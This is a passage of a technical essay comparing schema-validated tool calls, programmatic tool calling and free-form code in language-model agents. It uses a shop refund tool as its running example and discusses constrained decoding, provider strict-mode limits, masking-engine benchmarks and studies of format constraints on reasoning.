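# Schema-validated tool calls and free-form code in language-model agents: how the choice affects reliability

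## How agents act: tool calls, schemas and generated code

A language model only produces text, so ordinary software has to read that text and carry out any action it calls for, such as editing a file or transferring money. The software around the model is called the *harness*. An *agent* is a language model that works in a loop in which it chooses an action, receives the result and chooses again.

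Agents act in two main ways. In one, the model fills in a *tool call*, a structured request that names a single function from a predefined list and gives its arguments. A program can check that request against a written description of what the function accepts, and reject it before anything runs. In the other, the model writes code, usually Python or shell commands, and the harness runs it. Operations are easier to combine in code than in tool calls, but a program can check much less about code in advance. It is hard to say in general whether this makes code less reliable, partly because people often mean different kinds of failure when they ask.

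### The agent loop

For example, an online shop's support agent might have a tool named `issue_refund`. A customer writes that the blue mug in order A-1042 arrived broken and asks for a refund of its price. The mug cost $18.50, and the whole order came to $64.00.

1. The harness assembles a prompt from its standing instructions, a description of every tool the agent may use, and the customer's message.
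2. The model generates text. If it is going to act, the text contains a call to `issue_refund` in a format that the harness can recognise.
3. The harness parses the text and picks out the tool's name and arguments.
4. A *validator*, the program that accepts or rejects calls, compares the arguments with the tool's description.
5. If the call passes, the harness executes it, which here means that the shop's own payment code runs.
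6. The harness adds the result, or the error message, to the prompt and queries the model again.

The loop ends when the model answers with an ordinary message and no call.

*Better Models* (Ronacher, 2026) describes tool calls as text. The provider's server combines the conversation and the tool list into one long prompt with special markers. The model was trained on many examples of the format, and at some point it emits a pattern that the software interprets as a call. According to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, the model never runs anything on its own and never receives the tool's implementation. The only information the model has about `issue_refund` is its name, its description, the shape of its arguments and the results of earlier calls.

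*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the feedback step in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. Every call and output stays in the prompt until the harness has to condense the conversation to save space, and a single user request can set off hundreds of calls. If a call is rejected, the next prompt therefore includes the error and the model can try again, but retrying adds another round trip and makes the prompt longer.

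### A tool and its schema

The validator works from a *schema*, a machine-readable description of the arguments that a tool accepts. Most tools use JSON Schema, a standard vocabulary for describing data in JSON, which is a plain-text format of named fields and values. For the refund tool it might look like this:

```json
{
  "name": "issue_refund",
  "description": "Refund part or all of an order to the customer's card.",
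  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "order_id": { "type": "string", "description": "For example A-1042" },
      "amount_cents": { "type": "integer", "minimum": 1 },
      "reason": { "type": "string", "enum": ["damaged", "late", "wrong_item"] }
    },
    "required": ["order_id", "amount_cents", "reason"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

`type` sets the kind of value a field takes, so `amount_cents` must be a whole number, and `minimum` rules out refunds of zero or less. `enum` lists the only permitted values. `required` names the fields that must be present, and `additionalProperties: false` forbids fields the schema doesn't define, which JSON Schema otherwise allows. The `description` entries are only for the model, so a shop could write "never refund more than the item cost" there, but no validator would enforce it.

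This call passes:

```json
{
  "name": "issue_refund",
  "arguments": { "order_id": "A-1042", "amount_cents": 1850, "reason": "damaged" }
}
```

This one does not:

```json
{
  "name": "issue_refund",
  "arguments": { "order_id": "A-1042", "amount_cents": "18.50",
                 "reason": "damaged", "notify_customer": true }
}
```

The amount is a string where the schema requires an integer, and the schema doesn't define `notify_customer`. Real models make both mistakes. Anthropic's *Strict tool use* warns that Claude may supply `"2"` or `"two"` where a booking function needs the number 2. Ronacher ran into invented fields in July 2026 while debugging Pi, a coding harness whose file-editing tool takes a list of text replacements. Anthropic's Opus 4.8 sometimes added keys such as `requireUnique`, `matchCase` or `cost` to the entries in that list, and Pi rejected the calls and asked for a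 retry. In the calls he inspected, the replacement text itself was correct. A provider can also prevent such calls through *constrained decoding*, which blocks every token that would break the required format at each step of generation.

As code, the same refund takes an import and three lines:

```python
import shop

order = shop.get_order("A-1042")
mug = next(item for item in order.items if item.name == "blue mug")
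shop.refund(order.id, cents=mug.price_cents, note="damaged")
```

Here `shop` is the shop's own Python library. The script reads the mug's price from the order record, so the model does not have to copy 1850 correctly from the conversation. In a loop, the same lines could refund every customer whose mug came from a bad batch. But no schema checks the call in the last line before it reaches the payment system, and the script can also cancel orders or change prices if the library can.

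### Three designs on a scale

Schema-validated calls are at the strict end of a scale, and free-form scripts are at the other. The harness checks each validated call separately and returns its result to the model, whose output determines the next step. Looking up 20 orders takes 20 calls, and all 20 results are added to the prompt.

*Programmatic tool calling* falls between schema-validated tool calls and free-form code. The model writes a program that calls predefined, typed tools, and each call still leaves the program as a separate request. In the version described in Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling*, the model writes Python that treats every tool as a function. When the program reaches one of these functions, it pauses while the developer's application receives an ordinary tool call with a name and arguments, runs it and returns the result. The program then resumes. Intermediate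 results stay inside the program, so the model sees only the final output. In Anthropic's example of a budget check on 20 employees, one script makes all 20 lookups and returns only the people who overspent.

OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* describes the same idea in JavaScript. The runtime has no direct network access, no general-purpose file system and no way to start other processes, so a program can reach outside systems only through tools the developer has enabled. In the refund example, the last line of the script would become a call to `issue_refund` with the same three arguments, and the application could check them against the same schema. OpenAI tells developers to check arguments and permissions on every such call. It also advises them to keep writes and approval-sensitive actions as direct calls by default, and a refund is a write that many shops would want someone to approve.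 Under that advice, the program would look up orders and calculate amounts, and the model would then issue each refund in a separate direct call.

With free-form code, the harness gives the model a Python interpreter or a shell, runs whatever the model writes and returns the output. The code usually runs in a *sandbox*, an isolated environment that limits what the code can access.

A tool's position on this scale depends on how much its arguments can express, not on whether it uses JSON. Most shell commands arrive as tool calls too. The default `shell` tool that Bolin lists for Codex has a JSON Schema with a required `command` field and optional fields for the working directory and a time limit. A command that deletes a folder fits that schema as well as one that lists the folder's contents. The `query_database` tool in Anthropic's examples takes one string of SQL, the database query language,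 and that string can hold any query. OpenAI's *Function calling* also covers "custom tools", which accept free text. Because OpenAI allows programs to call a shell tool, a developer can turn the middle design into something close to free-form code by enabling that tool.

### Where the formats came from

Commercial function calling began on 13 June 2023, when OpenAI added it to its API. Developers could send JSON Schema definitions of their functions, and GPT-3.5 or GPT-4 would return JSON describing a function for the developer's code to execute (Willison, *OpenAI*, 2023). Wang, Chen and colleagues (2024) proposed CodeAct in *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents*. In CodeAct, every action on the environment is a piece of Python, and the model sees the interpreter's output or error message. They argued that models had seen a lot of code in training, and that agents with JSON actions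 could not combine several tools in one step. In November 2024 Anthropic released the Model Context Protocol (MCP), now the common standard for describing tools.

Before MCP, every new data source needed its own custom connector, as Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* explains. Under MCP, a company puts a *server* in front of its system, and any harness that contains an MCP *client* can use it. The client sends a `tools/list` request and gets back each tool's name, description and `inputSchema`, in the same form as the refund definition above. To call a tool, the client sends the server a `tools/call` request with the tool's name and arguments. The first specification, Model Context Protocol (2024), already required servers to validate all tool inputs, and Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) keeps the rule, but a client can't directly check whether a given server does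 so. In July 2026, Model Context Protocol (2026) reported close to half a billion downloads a month of its main software kits, and Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reported fourfold growth within the year.

### Four levels at which an action can be sound

A tool call can be valid in several senses. The attempts below all respond to the same request, to refund $18.50 for the broken mug, and each fails at a different level.

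| Level | A refund that fails there | What goes wrong |
|---|---|---|
| It parses | `{"order_id": "A-1042", "amount_cents": 1850,` | The text breaks off, and no parser can read it as JSON. |
| It fits the schema | Order A-1042, amount `"18.50"`, damaged | The amount is a string, and the validator rejects the call. |
| It can run in the present state | Order A-1042, amount `1850`, damaged | A colleague refunded the whole order yesterday, so the payment system refuses. |
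| It is what the user wanted | Order A-1042, amount `6400`, damaged | The customer gets the whole order back instead of the mug. Every check passes. |

A parser and a validator use only the text of the call and the schema. Whether order A-1042 still has money left to refund depends on the shop's records, so code with access to those records has to check it. *Input Validation Errors as Tool Execution Errors* (fredericbarthelet, 2025), a proposal that MCP has since adopted, gives a similar example. The schema of a flight-booking tool can require a date in the form dd/mm/yyyy, but JSON Schema cannot require the date to be in the future. Under the older, ambiguous rules, a server could report the refusal as a protocol error, which never reached the model, and the code editor Cursor would typically send the same past date three times. Servers now return such refusals as tool results with an explanation,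 so the model can correct the date.

None of this stops the $64.00 refund. To catch it, a person or program has to compare the call with the customer's message before the money is sent. The Model Context Protocol recommends that a person always be able to deny a call.

Sigdel and Baral (2026), in *Schema First Tool APIs for LLM Agents*, counted these failures separately, except that they combined parsing and schema errors. They gave debugging tasks to a very small model, Qwen2.5 with half a billion parameters, and described its tools either in prose or in JSON Schema with the same content. With schemas, the mean number of invalid calls fell from 5.39 to 3.72, and the mean number of execution failures fell from 0.54 to zero. Calls that fitted the schema but did not help with the task rose from 0.93 to 3.03. Part of that rise is probably due to the counting method, since a call has to pass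 the schema before it can count as valid but unhelpful. The model solved no task in any condition and is far weaker than anything a company would use today, so I find the study useful for how it separates failures rather than for its numbers.

An action can also fail at one level and succeed at the next. For example, the edits that Opus 4.8 sent to Pi broke the schema but contained the correct change.

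Generated code goes through the same levels of checking as a tool call, except for the schema check. Python parses the whole script before running any of it, so a syntax error stops the script before the first line runs. But a free-form script has no list of permitted arguments to check against. If an order has no money left to refund, the error appears only when the script reaches that order, perhaps after it has refunded ten others.

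People also use three words loosely when comparing calls and code. *Determinism* here means that the same request, from the same starting state, leads to the same actions and outcome every time the agent runs. An *error rate* is the share of attempted actions that fail at one named level, because the figure is unclear without the level. *Flexibility* is the range of work an agent can do, including combining tools within a single action, without a developer first building a tool for it.

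## Two ways to enforce a schema: rejecting bad calls and preventing them

A harness can enforce a schema by checking each finished call and asking for another when the check fails. It can also use constrained decoding, which prevents the model from writing an invalid call. Both methods produce schema-valid calls, but how often each valid call appears depends on the method. Providers' guarantees for constrained decoding also have gaps, so the harness still needs a validator.

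### Validate and retry

In validate-and-retry, a rejected call goes back to the model with an error message. This works with any model, without support from the model's provider, and the validator can enforce everything in JSON Schema, including conditional rules such as "a refund for `wrong_item` must include a photo".

The simplest version, rejection sampling, discards the failed attempt and samples again from the same prompt. Park, Wang and colleagues (2024), in *Grammar-Aligned Decoding*, point out that this method is exact, meaning that valid outputs keep the relative probabilities the model gave them. It is also impractically slow when nearly all of the model's outputs are invalid. Harnesses that return the error message lose this exactness because they change the prompt, but the message can lead the model to write something different.

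### How constrained decoding works

A model generates text one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. At each step it assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the software around it picks one at random according to those probabilities. Constrained decoding intervenes just before the software picks a token.

First, the provider compiles the schema into a grammar, a set of rules that defines every text the schema accepts. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API* (2024), the company chose context-free grammars because the simpler finite-state machines that some other tools use cannot, in general, keep track of brackets nested to any depth. Compiling makes the first request with a new schema slower, but the provider then caches the result for later requests.

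During generation, a program tests every token in the vocabulary. The question is whether the text so far, plus this token, could still grow into a valid call. *Mitigating Errors in LLM-Generated Web API Invocations* (2026) describes the result as a mask, a list with a one for each permitted token and a zero for each forbidden one. The software multiplies the model's probabilities by the mask and rescales what remains so that it adds up to one:

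```
P_masked(t | x) = P(t | x) · m(x, t) / Σ_u P(u | x) · m(x, u)
```

Here `x` is the prompt and everything generated so far, `t` is the candidate token, `m` is its entry in the mask, and the sum runs over all tokens `u`. The program has to compute a new mask after every token because the set of valid tokens changes. For example, an opening brace is valid at the start of a call but not in the middle of a field name.

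Suppose the refund call has reached `"amount_cents":` and the model assigns probabilities of 0.30 to a quotation mark, 0.60 to the digit 1 and 0.10 to the digit 6. The schema requires an integer, so the mask removes the quotation mark. Dividing the remaining probabilities by their sum, 0.70, gives the digit 1 about 0.86 and the digit 6 about 0.14. If the 1 begins 1850 and the 6 begins 6400, the mask has ruled out an amount of the wrong type, but the model can still refund the wrong amount. *Constrained Decoding Eliminates Structural Failures in Small LLMs* (2026) calls this remaining problem a semantic gap.

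### Why the two methods produce different calls

The mask checks only whether a valid ending exists, not how likely the model is to reach it, which can badly distort the result.

Suppose a customer's parcel came two weeks late, and the refund tool accepts three reasons: `damaged`, `late` and `wrong_item`. Suppose also that each letter is a token and that the model has a strong tendency to write "delayed", which the schema does not accept. The model starts with "d" with probability 0.9 (opening A). After "d", it completes a permitted value, `damaged`, only 1% of the time. It starts with "l" with probability 0.1 (opening B). After "l", it always completes `late`.

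If retries are independent, each attempt produces `damaged` with probability 0.9 × 0.01 = 0.009, produces `late` with probability 0.1, and otherwise fails. An attempt therefore passes with probability 0.109, so the harness makes about nine attempts (1 / 0.109) on average. About 92% of the calls that pass (0.1 / 0.109) have `late` as the reason.

With masking, the first attempt always passes. But "d" and "l" can both begin a valid value, so the mask leaves their probabilities at 0.9 and 0.1. Once the model has written "d", the mask blocks the "e" of "delayed" and forces the text towards `damaged`.

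| | Opening A: "d" | Opening B: "l" |
|---|---|---|
| Model's probability | 0.9 | 0.1 |
| Share of continuations that are valid | 1% | 100% |
| Share of accepted calls, independent retries | 8% | 92% |
| Share of calls, masking | 90% | 10% |

Masking therefore records nine out of ten late parcels as damaged, in calls that pass every check. The numbers are deliberately extreme. Real tokens usually span several letters, and a good model that has the three permitted values in its prompt would rarely start writing "delayed". The two methods give almost the same results when nearly everything the model writes is valid anyway, but they diverge when the model tends to write values the schema forbids, which is also when a developer most needs enforcement.

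To sample exactly, the software would have to replace the ones and zeros of the mask with the probability `c` that the model, left alone, would go on to finish a valid call:

```
P_exact(t | x) = P(t | x) · c(x, t) / Σ_u P(u | x) · c(x, u)
```

For the late parcel, `c` is 0.01 after "d" and 1 after "l", so the formula again gives 92%. Park and colleagues call `c` the expected future grammaticality, and *Attention Meets Reachability* (2026) derives the same correction under the name "survival probability". Masking effectively rounds every `c` above zero up to one. Computing `c` is intractable because it depends on every possible continuation.

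Park and colleagues named the task of sampling from the exact distribution *grammar-aligned decoding*. In their example, the grammar accepts 00000 and any five-digit binary string that starts with 1, and the prompt asks for a binary string that ends in 1. Mixtral, an open model from 2023, produced a string ending in 1 about 90% of the time without a constraint and 30% of the time under masking. The rate fell because after a first digit of 0, the mask allowed only 00000. Their algorithm, ASAp, starts as ordinary masking and records how much probability the mask removes along each path. It uses this record to lower its estimates of `c` for the next sample, and over many samples it converges on the exact distribution.

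An agent can rarely draw many samples for the same prompt, since it needs one call now and its prompt will be different at the next step. Later work has looked for corrections that require less computation. *Approximately Aligned Decoding* (Melcer, Gonugondla and colleagues, 2025) accepts some distortion in exchange for less resampling. *GrammarRL* (2026) keeps the mask on while training the model and rewards good finished outputs. *The Parser Already Knows* (Özgü, Wu and colleagues, 2026) trains a small separate model to estimate `c` from the candidate token and the current position in the grammar, both of which the masking software already has. This model is fitted once for each grammar and language model, using 1,000 unconstrained outputs. In tests on SQL queries and bit-vector formulas, the corrected distribution was four to five times closer to the exact one than plain masking was, by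 a standard measure of distance between distributions, and generation took at most 1.25 times as long. ASAp ran up to 20 times slower than masking and ended up further from the exact distribution.

None of these tests used tool schemas, so they reveal little about how often masking distorts an agent's calls. *Don't Adapt Small Language Models for Tools* (2025) comes closer, restricting small Qwen2.5 models to a list of valid tool names plus options such as "None". On one benchmark, the 7-billion-parameter model's share of correct tool choices rose from 49.5% to 78.1%, since it could no longer get the format wrong. On a test of whether a model refrains from calling a tool when none fits, the 3-billion-parameter model fell from 83.6% to 60.9%, probably because the list made it more likely to name a tool. These are small models from 2024, but OpenAI warns of a related problem in its current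 guide, *Structured outputs*. If the input has nothing to do with the schema, the model may invent values to fill it. OpenAI suggests telling the model what to return in that case.

Requiring a format may also make a model reason worse. *The Format Tax* (Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick, 2026) attributes most of this loss to the format instructions in the prompt and only a small part to the token mask.

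### What OpenAI and Anthropic guarantee

OpenAI introduced its schema guarantee in August 2024. On OpenAI's own test of complex schemas, a new version of GPT-4o with constrained decoding matched the schema 100% of the time, while a GPT-4 version from June 2023 did so less than 40% of the time. Most of that gain came from training, since the new model reached 93% without constrained decoding.

Anthropic and OpenAI now offer constrained decoding for tool arguments as *strict mode*, which a developer turns on by adding `strict: true` to a tool's definition. Anthropic promises that the arguments will follow the schema and that the tool name will match one of the tools provided, and says developers no longer need to validate and retry. OpenAI recommends always enabling strict mode.

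Developers can still run without strict mode and not notice. If a request to OpenAI's newer Responses interface omits the setting, OpenAI tries to convert the schema into a form that strict mode accepts. If that fails, it falls back to best effort, and the only sign is `strict: false` in the response. The older Chat Completions interface leaves strict mode off by default. When strict mode was new, Willison passed on three reasons from OpenAI's Ted Sanders for not making it the default: the first request with each schema is slow, some schemas fall outside the subset that OpenAI supports, and failures become rarer but more catastrophic, because a model that goes wrong can get stuck in a loop of technically valid output.

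The supported subset matters a lot in practice. The table is based on OpenAI's current guide and Anthropic's *Structured outputs*, whose limits also apply to strict tools.

| Schema feature | OpenAI | Anthropic |
|---|---|---|
| Numeric rules (`minimum`, `maximum`, `multipleOf`) | Yes, except on fine-tuned models | No |
| String length (`minLength`, `maxLength`) | Not on the supported list | No |
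| Text patterns (`pattern`) | Yes, except on fine-tuned models | Simple patterns only |
| Array length | `minItems` and `maxItems`, except on fine-tuned models | `minItems` of 0 or 1 only |
| Schemas that refer to themselves | Yes | No |
| Optional fields | None; a field can accept null instead | Up to 24 per request |
| Undeclared fields | Always forbidden | Always forbidden |
| Main size limits | 5,000 properties, 10 levels of nesting and 1,000 enum values per schema | 20 strict tools and 16 fields with alternative types per request |

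Neither OpenAI nor Anthropic lists JSON Schema's conditional keywords, `if`, `then` and `else`, as supported. In strict mode, both return an error when a schema contains something they don't support, so the developer has to remove the rule from the schema and enforce it elsewhere. The refund tool's schema, for example, contains `"minimum": 1`, which OpenAI's standard models enforce and Anthropic rejects. To use strict mode with Claude, the shop has to delete that line. A refund of zero or minus 1,850 cents then fits the schema, and the shop's own code has to catch it. Anthropic's software development kits can rewrite an unsupported schema automatically, and for structured answers its Python kit also validates the response after it arrives.

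Anthropic's size limits apply to a whole request, so four strict tools with six optional fields each reach the limit of 24 optional fields. Each optional field roughly doubles part of the compiled grammar, and fields with alternative types enlarge it even more. A developer who copies OpenAI's workaround of accepting null may therefore reach Anthropic's limit of 16 fields with alternative types instead. Even schemas within all these limits can fail if the combined grammar is too large or takes more than 180 seconds to compile. An agent connected to several MCP servers can easily have more than 20 tools, and the people who wrote those servers chose the schemas. Anthropic first advises making only the critical tools strict.

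Even a schema within the limits does not guarantee a valid call. If the model refuses a request for safety reasons, the refusal takes precedence over the schema. The request still counts as successful, so the harness has to check the response for a refusal marker. A call that hits the token limit is cut off, like the unfinished refund call that no parser can read. The loops that Sanders described also end this way, because a mask can keep every token legal but cannot make the model finish. OpenAI still documents an example in JSON mode, an older setting that guarantees valid JSON but not a particular schema. Without an instruction in the prompt to produce JSON, the model may emit whitespace until it runs out of tokens.

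Anthropic also notes that strict mode does not guarantee the capitalisation of enum values. A schema might permit "Conversation topic 3", and Claude might return "Conversation Topic 3" without any error or marker. A harness that compares strings exactly would then find no match. The promise that strict mode makes validation unnecessary is therefore too strong. Checking calls against the full schema with an ordinary validator adds almost no overhead, and it catches capitalisation errors, truncated calls and violations of any rules the developer had to remove to use strict mode.

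Constrained decoding also works for formats other than JSON. OpenAI lets developers restrict the input to its free-text custom tools with a grammar or a regular expression, so a tool could accept only a narrow kind of database query, for example. OpenAI warns that an overly complex grammar can cause an error or lead the model to produce long, repetitive output that fits the grammar but has the wrong meaning.

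### How well open-source engines enforce schemas

Developers who run open models choose their own masking software, and its quality varies widely. In *JSONSchemaBench*, Geng, Cooper and colleagues (2025) collected almost 10,000 real schemas and tested four open-source masking engines and the services of OpenAI and Google. They distinguished *declared coverage*, the share of schemas that an engine accepts without an error, from *empirical coverage*, the share for which the output was valid. The open-source engines all ran the same small Llama model, with one billion parameters, and had 40 seconds to compile each schema and 40 more to generate output. The table gives empirical coverage for three of the collections.

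| Engine | Function-call schemas | GitHub schemas, 30–100 fields | GitHub schemas, 100–500 fields |
|---|---|---|---|
| None (model alone) | 90% | 38% | 13% |
| Guidance | 96% | 69% | 41% |
| llama.cpp | 95% | 57% | 39% |
| XGrammar | 93% | 52% | 28% |
| Outlines | 95% | 29% | 3% |
| OpenAI | 89% | 12% | 9% |

On schemas written for function calls, the engines hardly differ, and even a tiny unconstrained model gets nine in ten right. The engines differ more on large schemas, where Outlines did worse than the unconstrained model, mainly because it ran out of time. OpenAI's figures are low because it refused some schemas up front. Among the schemas it accepted, the output was valid for 92% in the middle collection and for all of them in the largest. OpenAI also ran its own models, so its row isn't strictly comparable with the others.

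Geng and colleagues then ran the open-source engines on the official JSON Schema test suite, which covers 45 groups of features. An engine can fail by blocking valid data or by allowing invalid data. XGrammar had compile errors in only 3 groups but let invalid data through in 38, while Guidance had compile errors in 25 and let invalid data through in 1. Letting invalid data through is worse for an agent, because a developer who gets an error at least knows that the guarantee is missing. These results are almost two years old, so they are a better guide to how engines fail than to which engine is best now.

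Reliability also depends on which grammar is used for masking. *Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding via Parser Stack Classification* (2026) compared a general JSON grammar, which only keeps the brackets and quotation marks in order, with grammars built from each schema. On about 100 tasks, the schema-specific grammars did significantly better for every model, and the general grammar still did better than no constraint.

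Masking can make generation faster or slower, depending on the implementation. For function-call schemas, Geng and colleagues measured 15.4 milliseconds per token without a constraint, 6.4 with Guidance, and about 30 with either Outlines or llama.cpp. Guidance saves time when the grammar allows only one continuation, such as the rest of a required field's name, because it inserts that text without running the model.

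### The Pi edit tool

The best-documented recent case of a strong model breaking a schema is one that Ronacher debugged in Pi. Each entry in the editing tool's list of replacements should have exactly two fields, `oldText` and `newText`. Opus 4.8 and Claude Sonnet 5 sometimes added a third field to an otherwise correct edit. Ronacher saw dozens of invented field names, including `oldText2` and `event.0.additionalProperties`. Anthropic's older models did not do this, nor did any of the OpenAI Codex models he tried.

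A fresh request to edit a file never triggered the fault. Ronacher could reproduce it only with another user's transcripts, in which the model had already read files, diagnosed a problem and written edits several lines long. When he continued that user's session, about 20% of Opus 4.8's calls failed. Removing the model's earlier reasoning from the history halved the failure rate, and turning on strict mode eliminated the failures in his runs.

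A 20% failure rate is inconvenient but manageable if retries work. If each attempt failed independently at that rate, completing 100 edits would take about 125 calls. But each of the 25 extra calls would repeat a multi-line edit in full, and every rejected call would stay in the prompt.

Strict mode works unusually well against this fault. The invented fields appeared just after the model had closed a long `newText` string, where it had to write either a closing brace or a comma and another field name. The schema allows only the brace there, so the mask blocks the error at its first token, when everything written so far is correct. With "delayed" and `damaged`, the mask acts only after the model has written the shared "d", which is too late.

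Ronacher's hypothesis about the cause is that Anthropic trains its newer models inside Claude Code, its own coding harness, or something very like it. Claude Code's editing tool has a flat format with a path, an old string, a new string and an optional `replace_all` setting. A model trained on that tool might learn that an edit can carry one extra option. Pi's nested format has no such option, so the model would have no learned name for it and would make one up each time. This would explain why the invented names vary so much and why only the newer models produce them. But nobody outside Anthropic can inspect the training, and the 20% figure comes from one user's session. Ronacher also left out Claude Fable, so his result doesn't show whether Anthropic's strongest models share the fault.

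### Harnesses that repair calls silently

Claude Code handles bad calls in a third way, by fixing them. Ronacher read its compressed source and found that it accepts several names for the same argument, converts values to the expected type, repairs broken Unicode sequences and drops fields it doesn't recognise, mostly without telling the model. A call with a stray `requireUnique` would therefore succeed. Claude Code does not use strict mode, and Ronacher presumes this is because of Anthropic's complexity limits.

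When an edit is otherwise correct, repairing the call takes the least work because it requires no retry and no compiled grammar. If Ronacher is right about the training, though, the repairs also contribute to the malformed calls. Rewarding a model despite a malformed call does little to discourage more of them, and those calls then cause errors in other harnesses with stricter validators.

Repair is also riskier for some tools than for others. The rejected refund call from the first section had the amount `"18.50"` and an undeclared field, `notify_customer`, set to true. A harness that converts the amount to a whole number by cutting off the decimals would refund 18 cents. If it also drops the undeclared field, the shop sends no notification, but the agent receives a report of success and may tell the customer to expect one. A validator would have stopped this call if the harness had not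 repaired it.

A harness can safely rename `path` to `file_path` because the call has only one sensible reading. Rejection is worth the extra round trip when a repair would mean guessing an amount or discarding a field that might have changed what the call does. When a harness repairs a call, it can log the change and include the call as executed in the result. The developer can then count the errors, and the model has a chance to notice, for example, that no notification was sent.

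## Whether a required format makes the model reason worse

Developers who enforce a schema usually expect it to change only how the model writes its answer, not which answer it reaches. Researchers have disagreed since 2024 about whether this is true. Much of the disagreement comes from experiments that switched from prose to JSON but also changed the prompt's wording, the order in which the model reasoned and answered, or the rule for counting an answer as correct.

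### The 2024 dispute

*Let Me Speak Freely?* (Tam, Wu and colleagues, 2024) tested five models on school mathematics problems and two kinds of puzzle. In one puzzle, Last Letter, the model joins the last letters of four names. The models answered in prose, in a format specified in the prompt, or in a provider's JSON mode. Accuracy on these tasks generally fell as the format rules became stricter. On classification tasks, such as choosing one of 49 diagnoses, JSON mode did about as well as prose and sometimes better.

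The order of the fields in the JSON output weakens the paper's main claim. On Last Letter, GPT-3.5 Turbo in JSON mode always wrote the `answer` field before the `reason` field. A model generates text in order, so reasoning that comes after the answer cannot improve it. When Tam and colleagues tried OpenAI's schema enforcement, then new, GPT-4o mini's score fell three points on the mathematics problems and rose three on Last Letter.

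In *Say What You Mean*, Kurt replied on behalf of .txt, the company that makes the masking engine Outlines. He examined the recorded data and found that the prose and JSON prompts were not equivalent. One JSON prompt told Llama 3 8B that it must use "the tool" without naming a tool, mentioning JSON or listing any fields. Kurt wrote a prompt that showed the required JSON and a worked example, then ran the same model on it with and without a mask. Accuracy on Last Letter was 77% with the mask and 73% without it. His company has an interest in that result, and his schema accepted only four capital letters as an answer, so it ruled out some wrong answers as well as malformed ones.

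He also showed how much the scoring rule affects results. The same recorded prose answers scored 35% when he accepted only one exact phrase and 61% when he also accepted variants such as "e-S-S-E".

Castillo (2024), in *The good, the bad, and the ugly of Gemini’s structured outputs*, reran the reasoning tasks on Gemini 1.5 Flash. Tam and colleagues had measured 89% on the mathematics problems in prose and 48% with an enforced schema. Castillo found that Google's Python SDK sorted the fields alphabetically, which put `answer` before `reasoning`. He renamed `answer` to `solution` so that it came after `reasoning`, and the model then scored 93.0% with the enforced schema and 93.7% in prose. A gap remained on the task of tracking objects through a series of swaps, where the model scored 86% with the schema and 97% in prose. Google's newer SDK seems to keep the fields in order.

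So the largest losses in the 2024 study came from prompts and field order. The swap puzzle suggests that something else also contributed, at least for that model.

### Asking for a format and enforcing it

*The Format Tax*, from April 2026, separates the effect of asking for a format from the effect of enforcing it. Lee and colleagues tested ten models on mathematics, graduate-level science, logic puzzles and writing, in JSON, XML, Markdown and LaTeX. On the three reasoning tasks, they ran each format prompt with and without a mask that enforced the format, and compared both results with those from a prompt that asked for no format.

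For the six open models, asking for the format lowered scores by an average of 3.9 percentage points, and masking lowered them by a further 1.6. The effect was statistically significant in 39 combinations of model, task and format, and in 36 of those it was already present without the mask.

Tool calls use JSON, so the table below averages only the JSON results, over the three reasoning tasks and with hidden reasoning switched off.

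| Model | Accuracy in prose | Change when the prompt asks for JSON | Change with the mask as well |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3 32B | 67.1% | −6.8 | −9.1 |
| Qwen3 8B | 62.5% | −8.3 | −12.1 |
| OLMo 3.1 32B | 72.7% | −2.0 | −2.5 |
| OLMo 3 7B | 67.7% | −5.3 | −9.1 |
| SmolLM3 3B | 42.9% | −5.9 | −7.4 |
| Nemotron 3 Nano | 56.2% | −2.2 | −3.1 |
| GPT-5 nano | 61.9% | −5.9 | −3.3 |
| GPT-5.4 nano | 70.8% | +4.7 | +1.5 |
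| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 78.6% | +1.5 | +1.6 |
| Grok 4.1 Fast | 72.9% | +1.9 | +4.3 |

Every open model lost accuracy, while the three newest closed models gained some. Part of the gain came from the logic puzzles, where a fixed template seems to have made GPT-5.4 nano and Grok work through the clues more carefully. Four closed models are too few to establish a general rule, but they show that the loss is avoidable.

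A request for JSON most likely hurts because the model writes less. Formatted answers were shorter than prose answers 71% of the time, with a median difference of 162 tokens. Right answers became wrong least often when the length stayed about the same, and more than 40% of the time when it changed most. Including examples or the full schema in the prompt did not close the gap.

Masking alone can still sharply reduce accuracy. With XML, GPT-5.4 nano lost less than 3 points on mathematics when it was prompted to use the format and 59 points when a mask enforced it. Under the mask, it filled the answer field with placeholders such as "Proceed to solve by algebraic constraints". Its predecessor, GPT-5 nano, handled the same XML mask well. Lee and colleagues suspect that OpenAI trained the newer model to work under JSON masks and that the training did not carry over to other grammars.

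### The 180-minute meeting

Ray (2026), in *The Constraint Tax*, tested much smaller models, the kind that can run on a phone or laptop. The main experiment covered three models with 0.5 to 1.7 billion parameters. With a mask, the share of schema-valid outputs rose from 61.5% to 100%, while the share of correct answers fell from 19.7% to 11.0%. Many of the correct answers in the unmasked runs were in broken JSON. Counting only correct answers in usable JSON, the share was 12.0% without the mask and 11.0% with it. But the share of outputs that were valid but wrong, which a validator cannot catch, rose from 49.5% to 88.9% with the mask.

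Ray's calendar test is harder to explain. Qwen2.5 with 1.5 billion parameters had to fill in a call to a calendar tool, giving a title, date, start time, duration, attendee and topic. All 200 calls in each run fitted the schema, whether the prompt only asked for JSON or a mask enforced the schema. But 183 calls (91.5%) were correct without the mask and only 96 (48.0%) with it. Of the 104 wrong calls in the masked run, 102 were wrong only in the duration. One masked call, for a 30-minute meeting with Leo, had the right date, time, attendee and topic but a duration of 180 minutes.

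Both modes asked for JSON, so the request itself can't explain the difference. Masking appears to have halved the accuracy of a tool call that the model could already format perfectly.

### A proof that masking cannot hurt, and its conditions

Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026), in *Constrained Decoding*, an October paper, prove that this should not happen under certain conditions. Let `x` be the prompt, `R` the reasoning the model has already written, and `y*` the correct answer, a sequence of `T` tokens. At step `t`, let `Z_t` be the total probability that the model gives to the tokens the mask permits. Masking divides the probability of each permitted token by `Z_t`, which over the whole answer gives:

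```
P_masked(y* | x, R) = P(y* | x, R) / (Z_1 · Z_2 · ... · Z_T) ≥ P(y* | x, R)
```

Each `Z_t` is greater than zero and at most one, so dividing by their product cannot lower the probability. If the mask blocks nothing the model might have written along the way, every `Z_t` is one and the probability stays the same.

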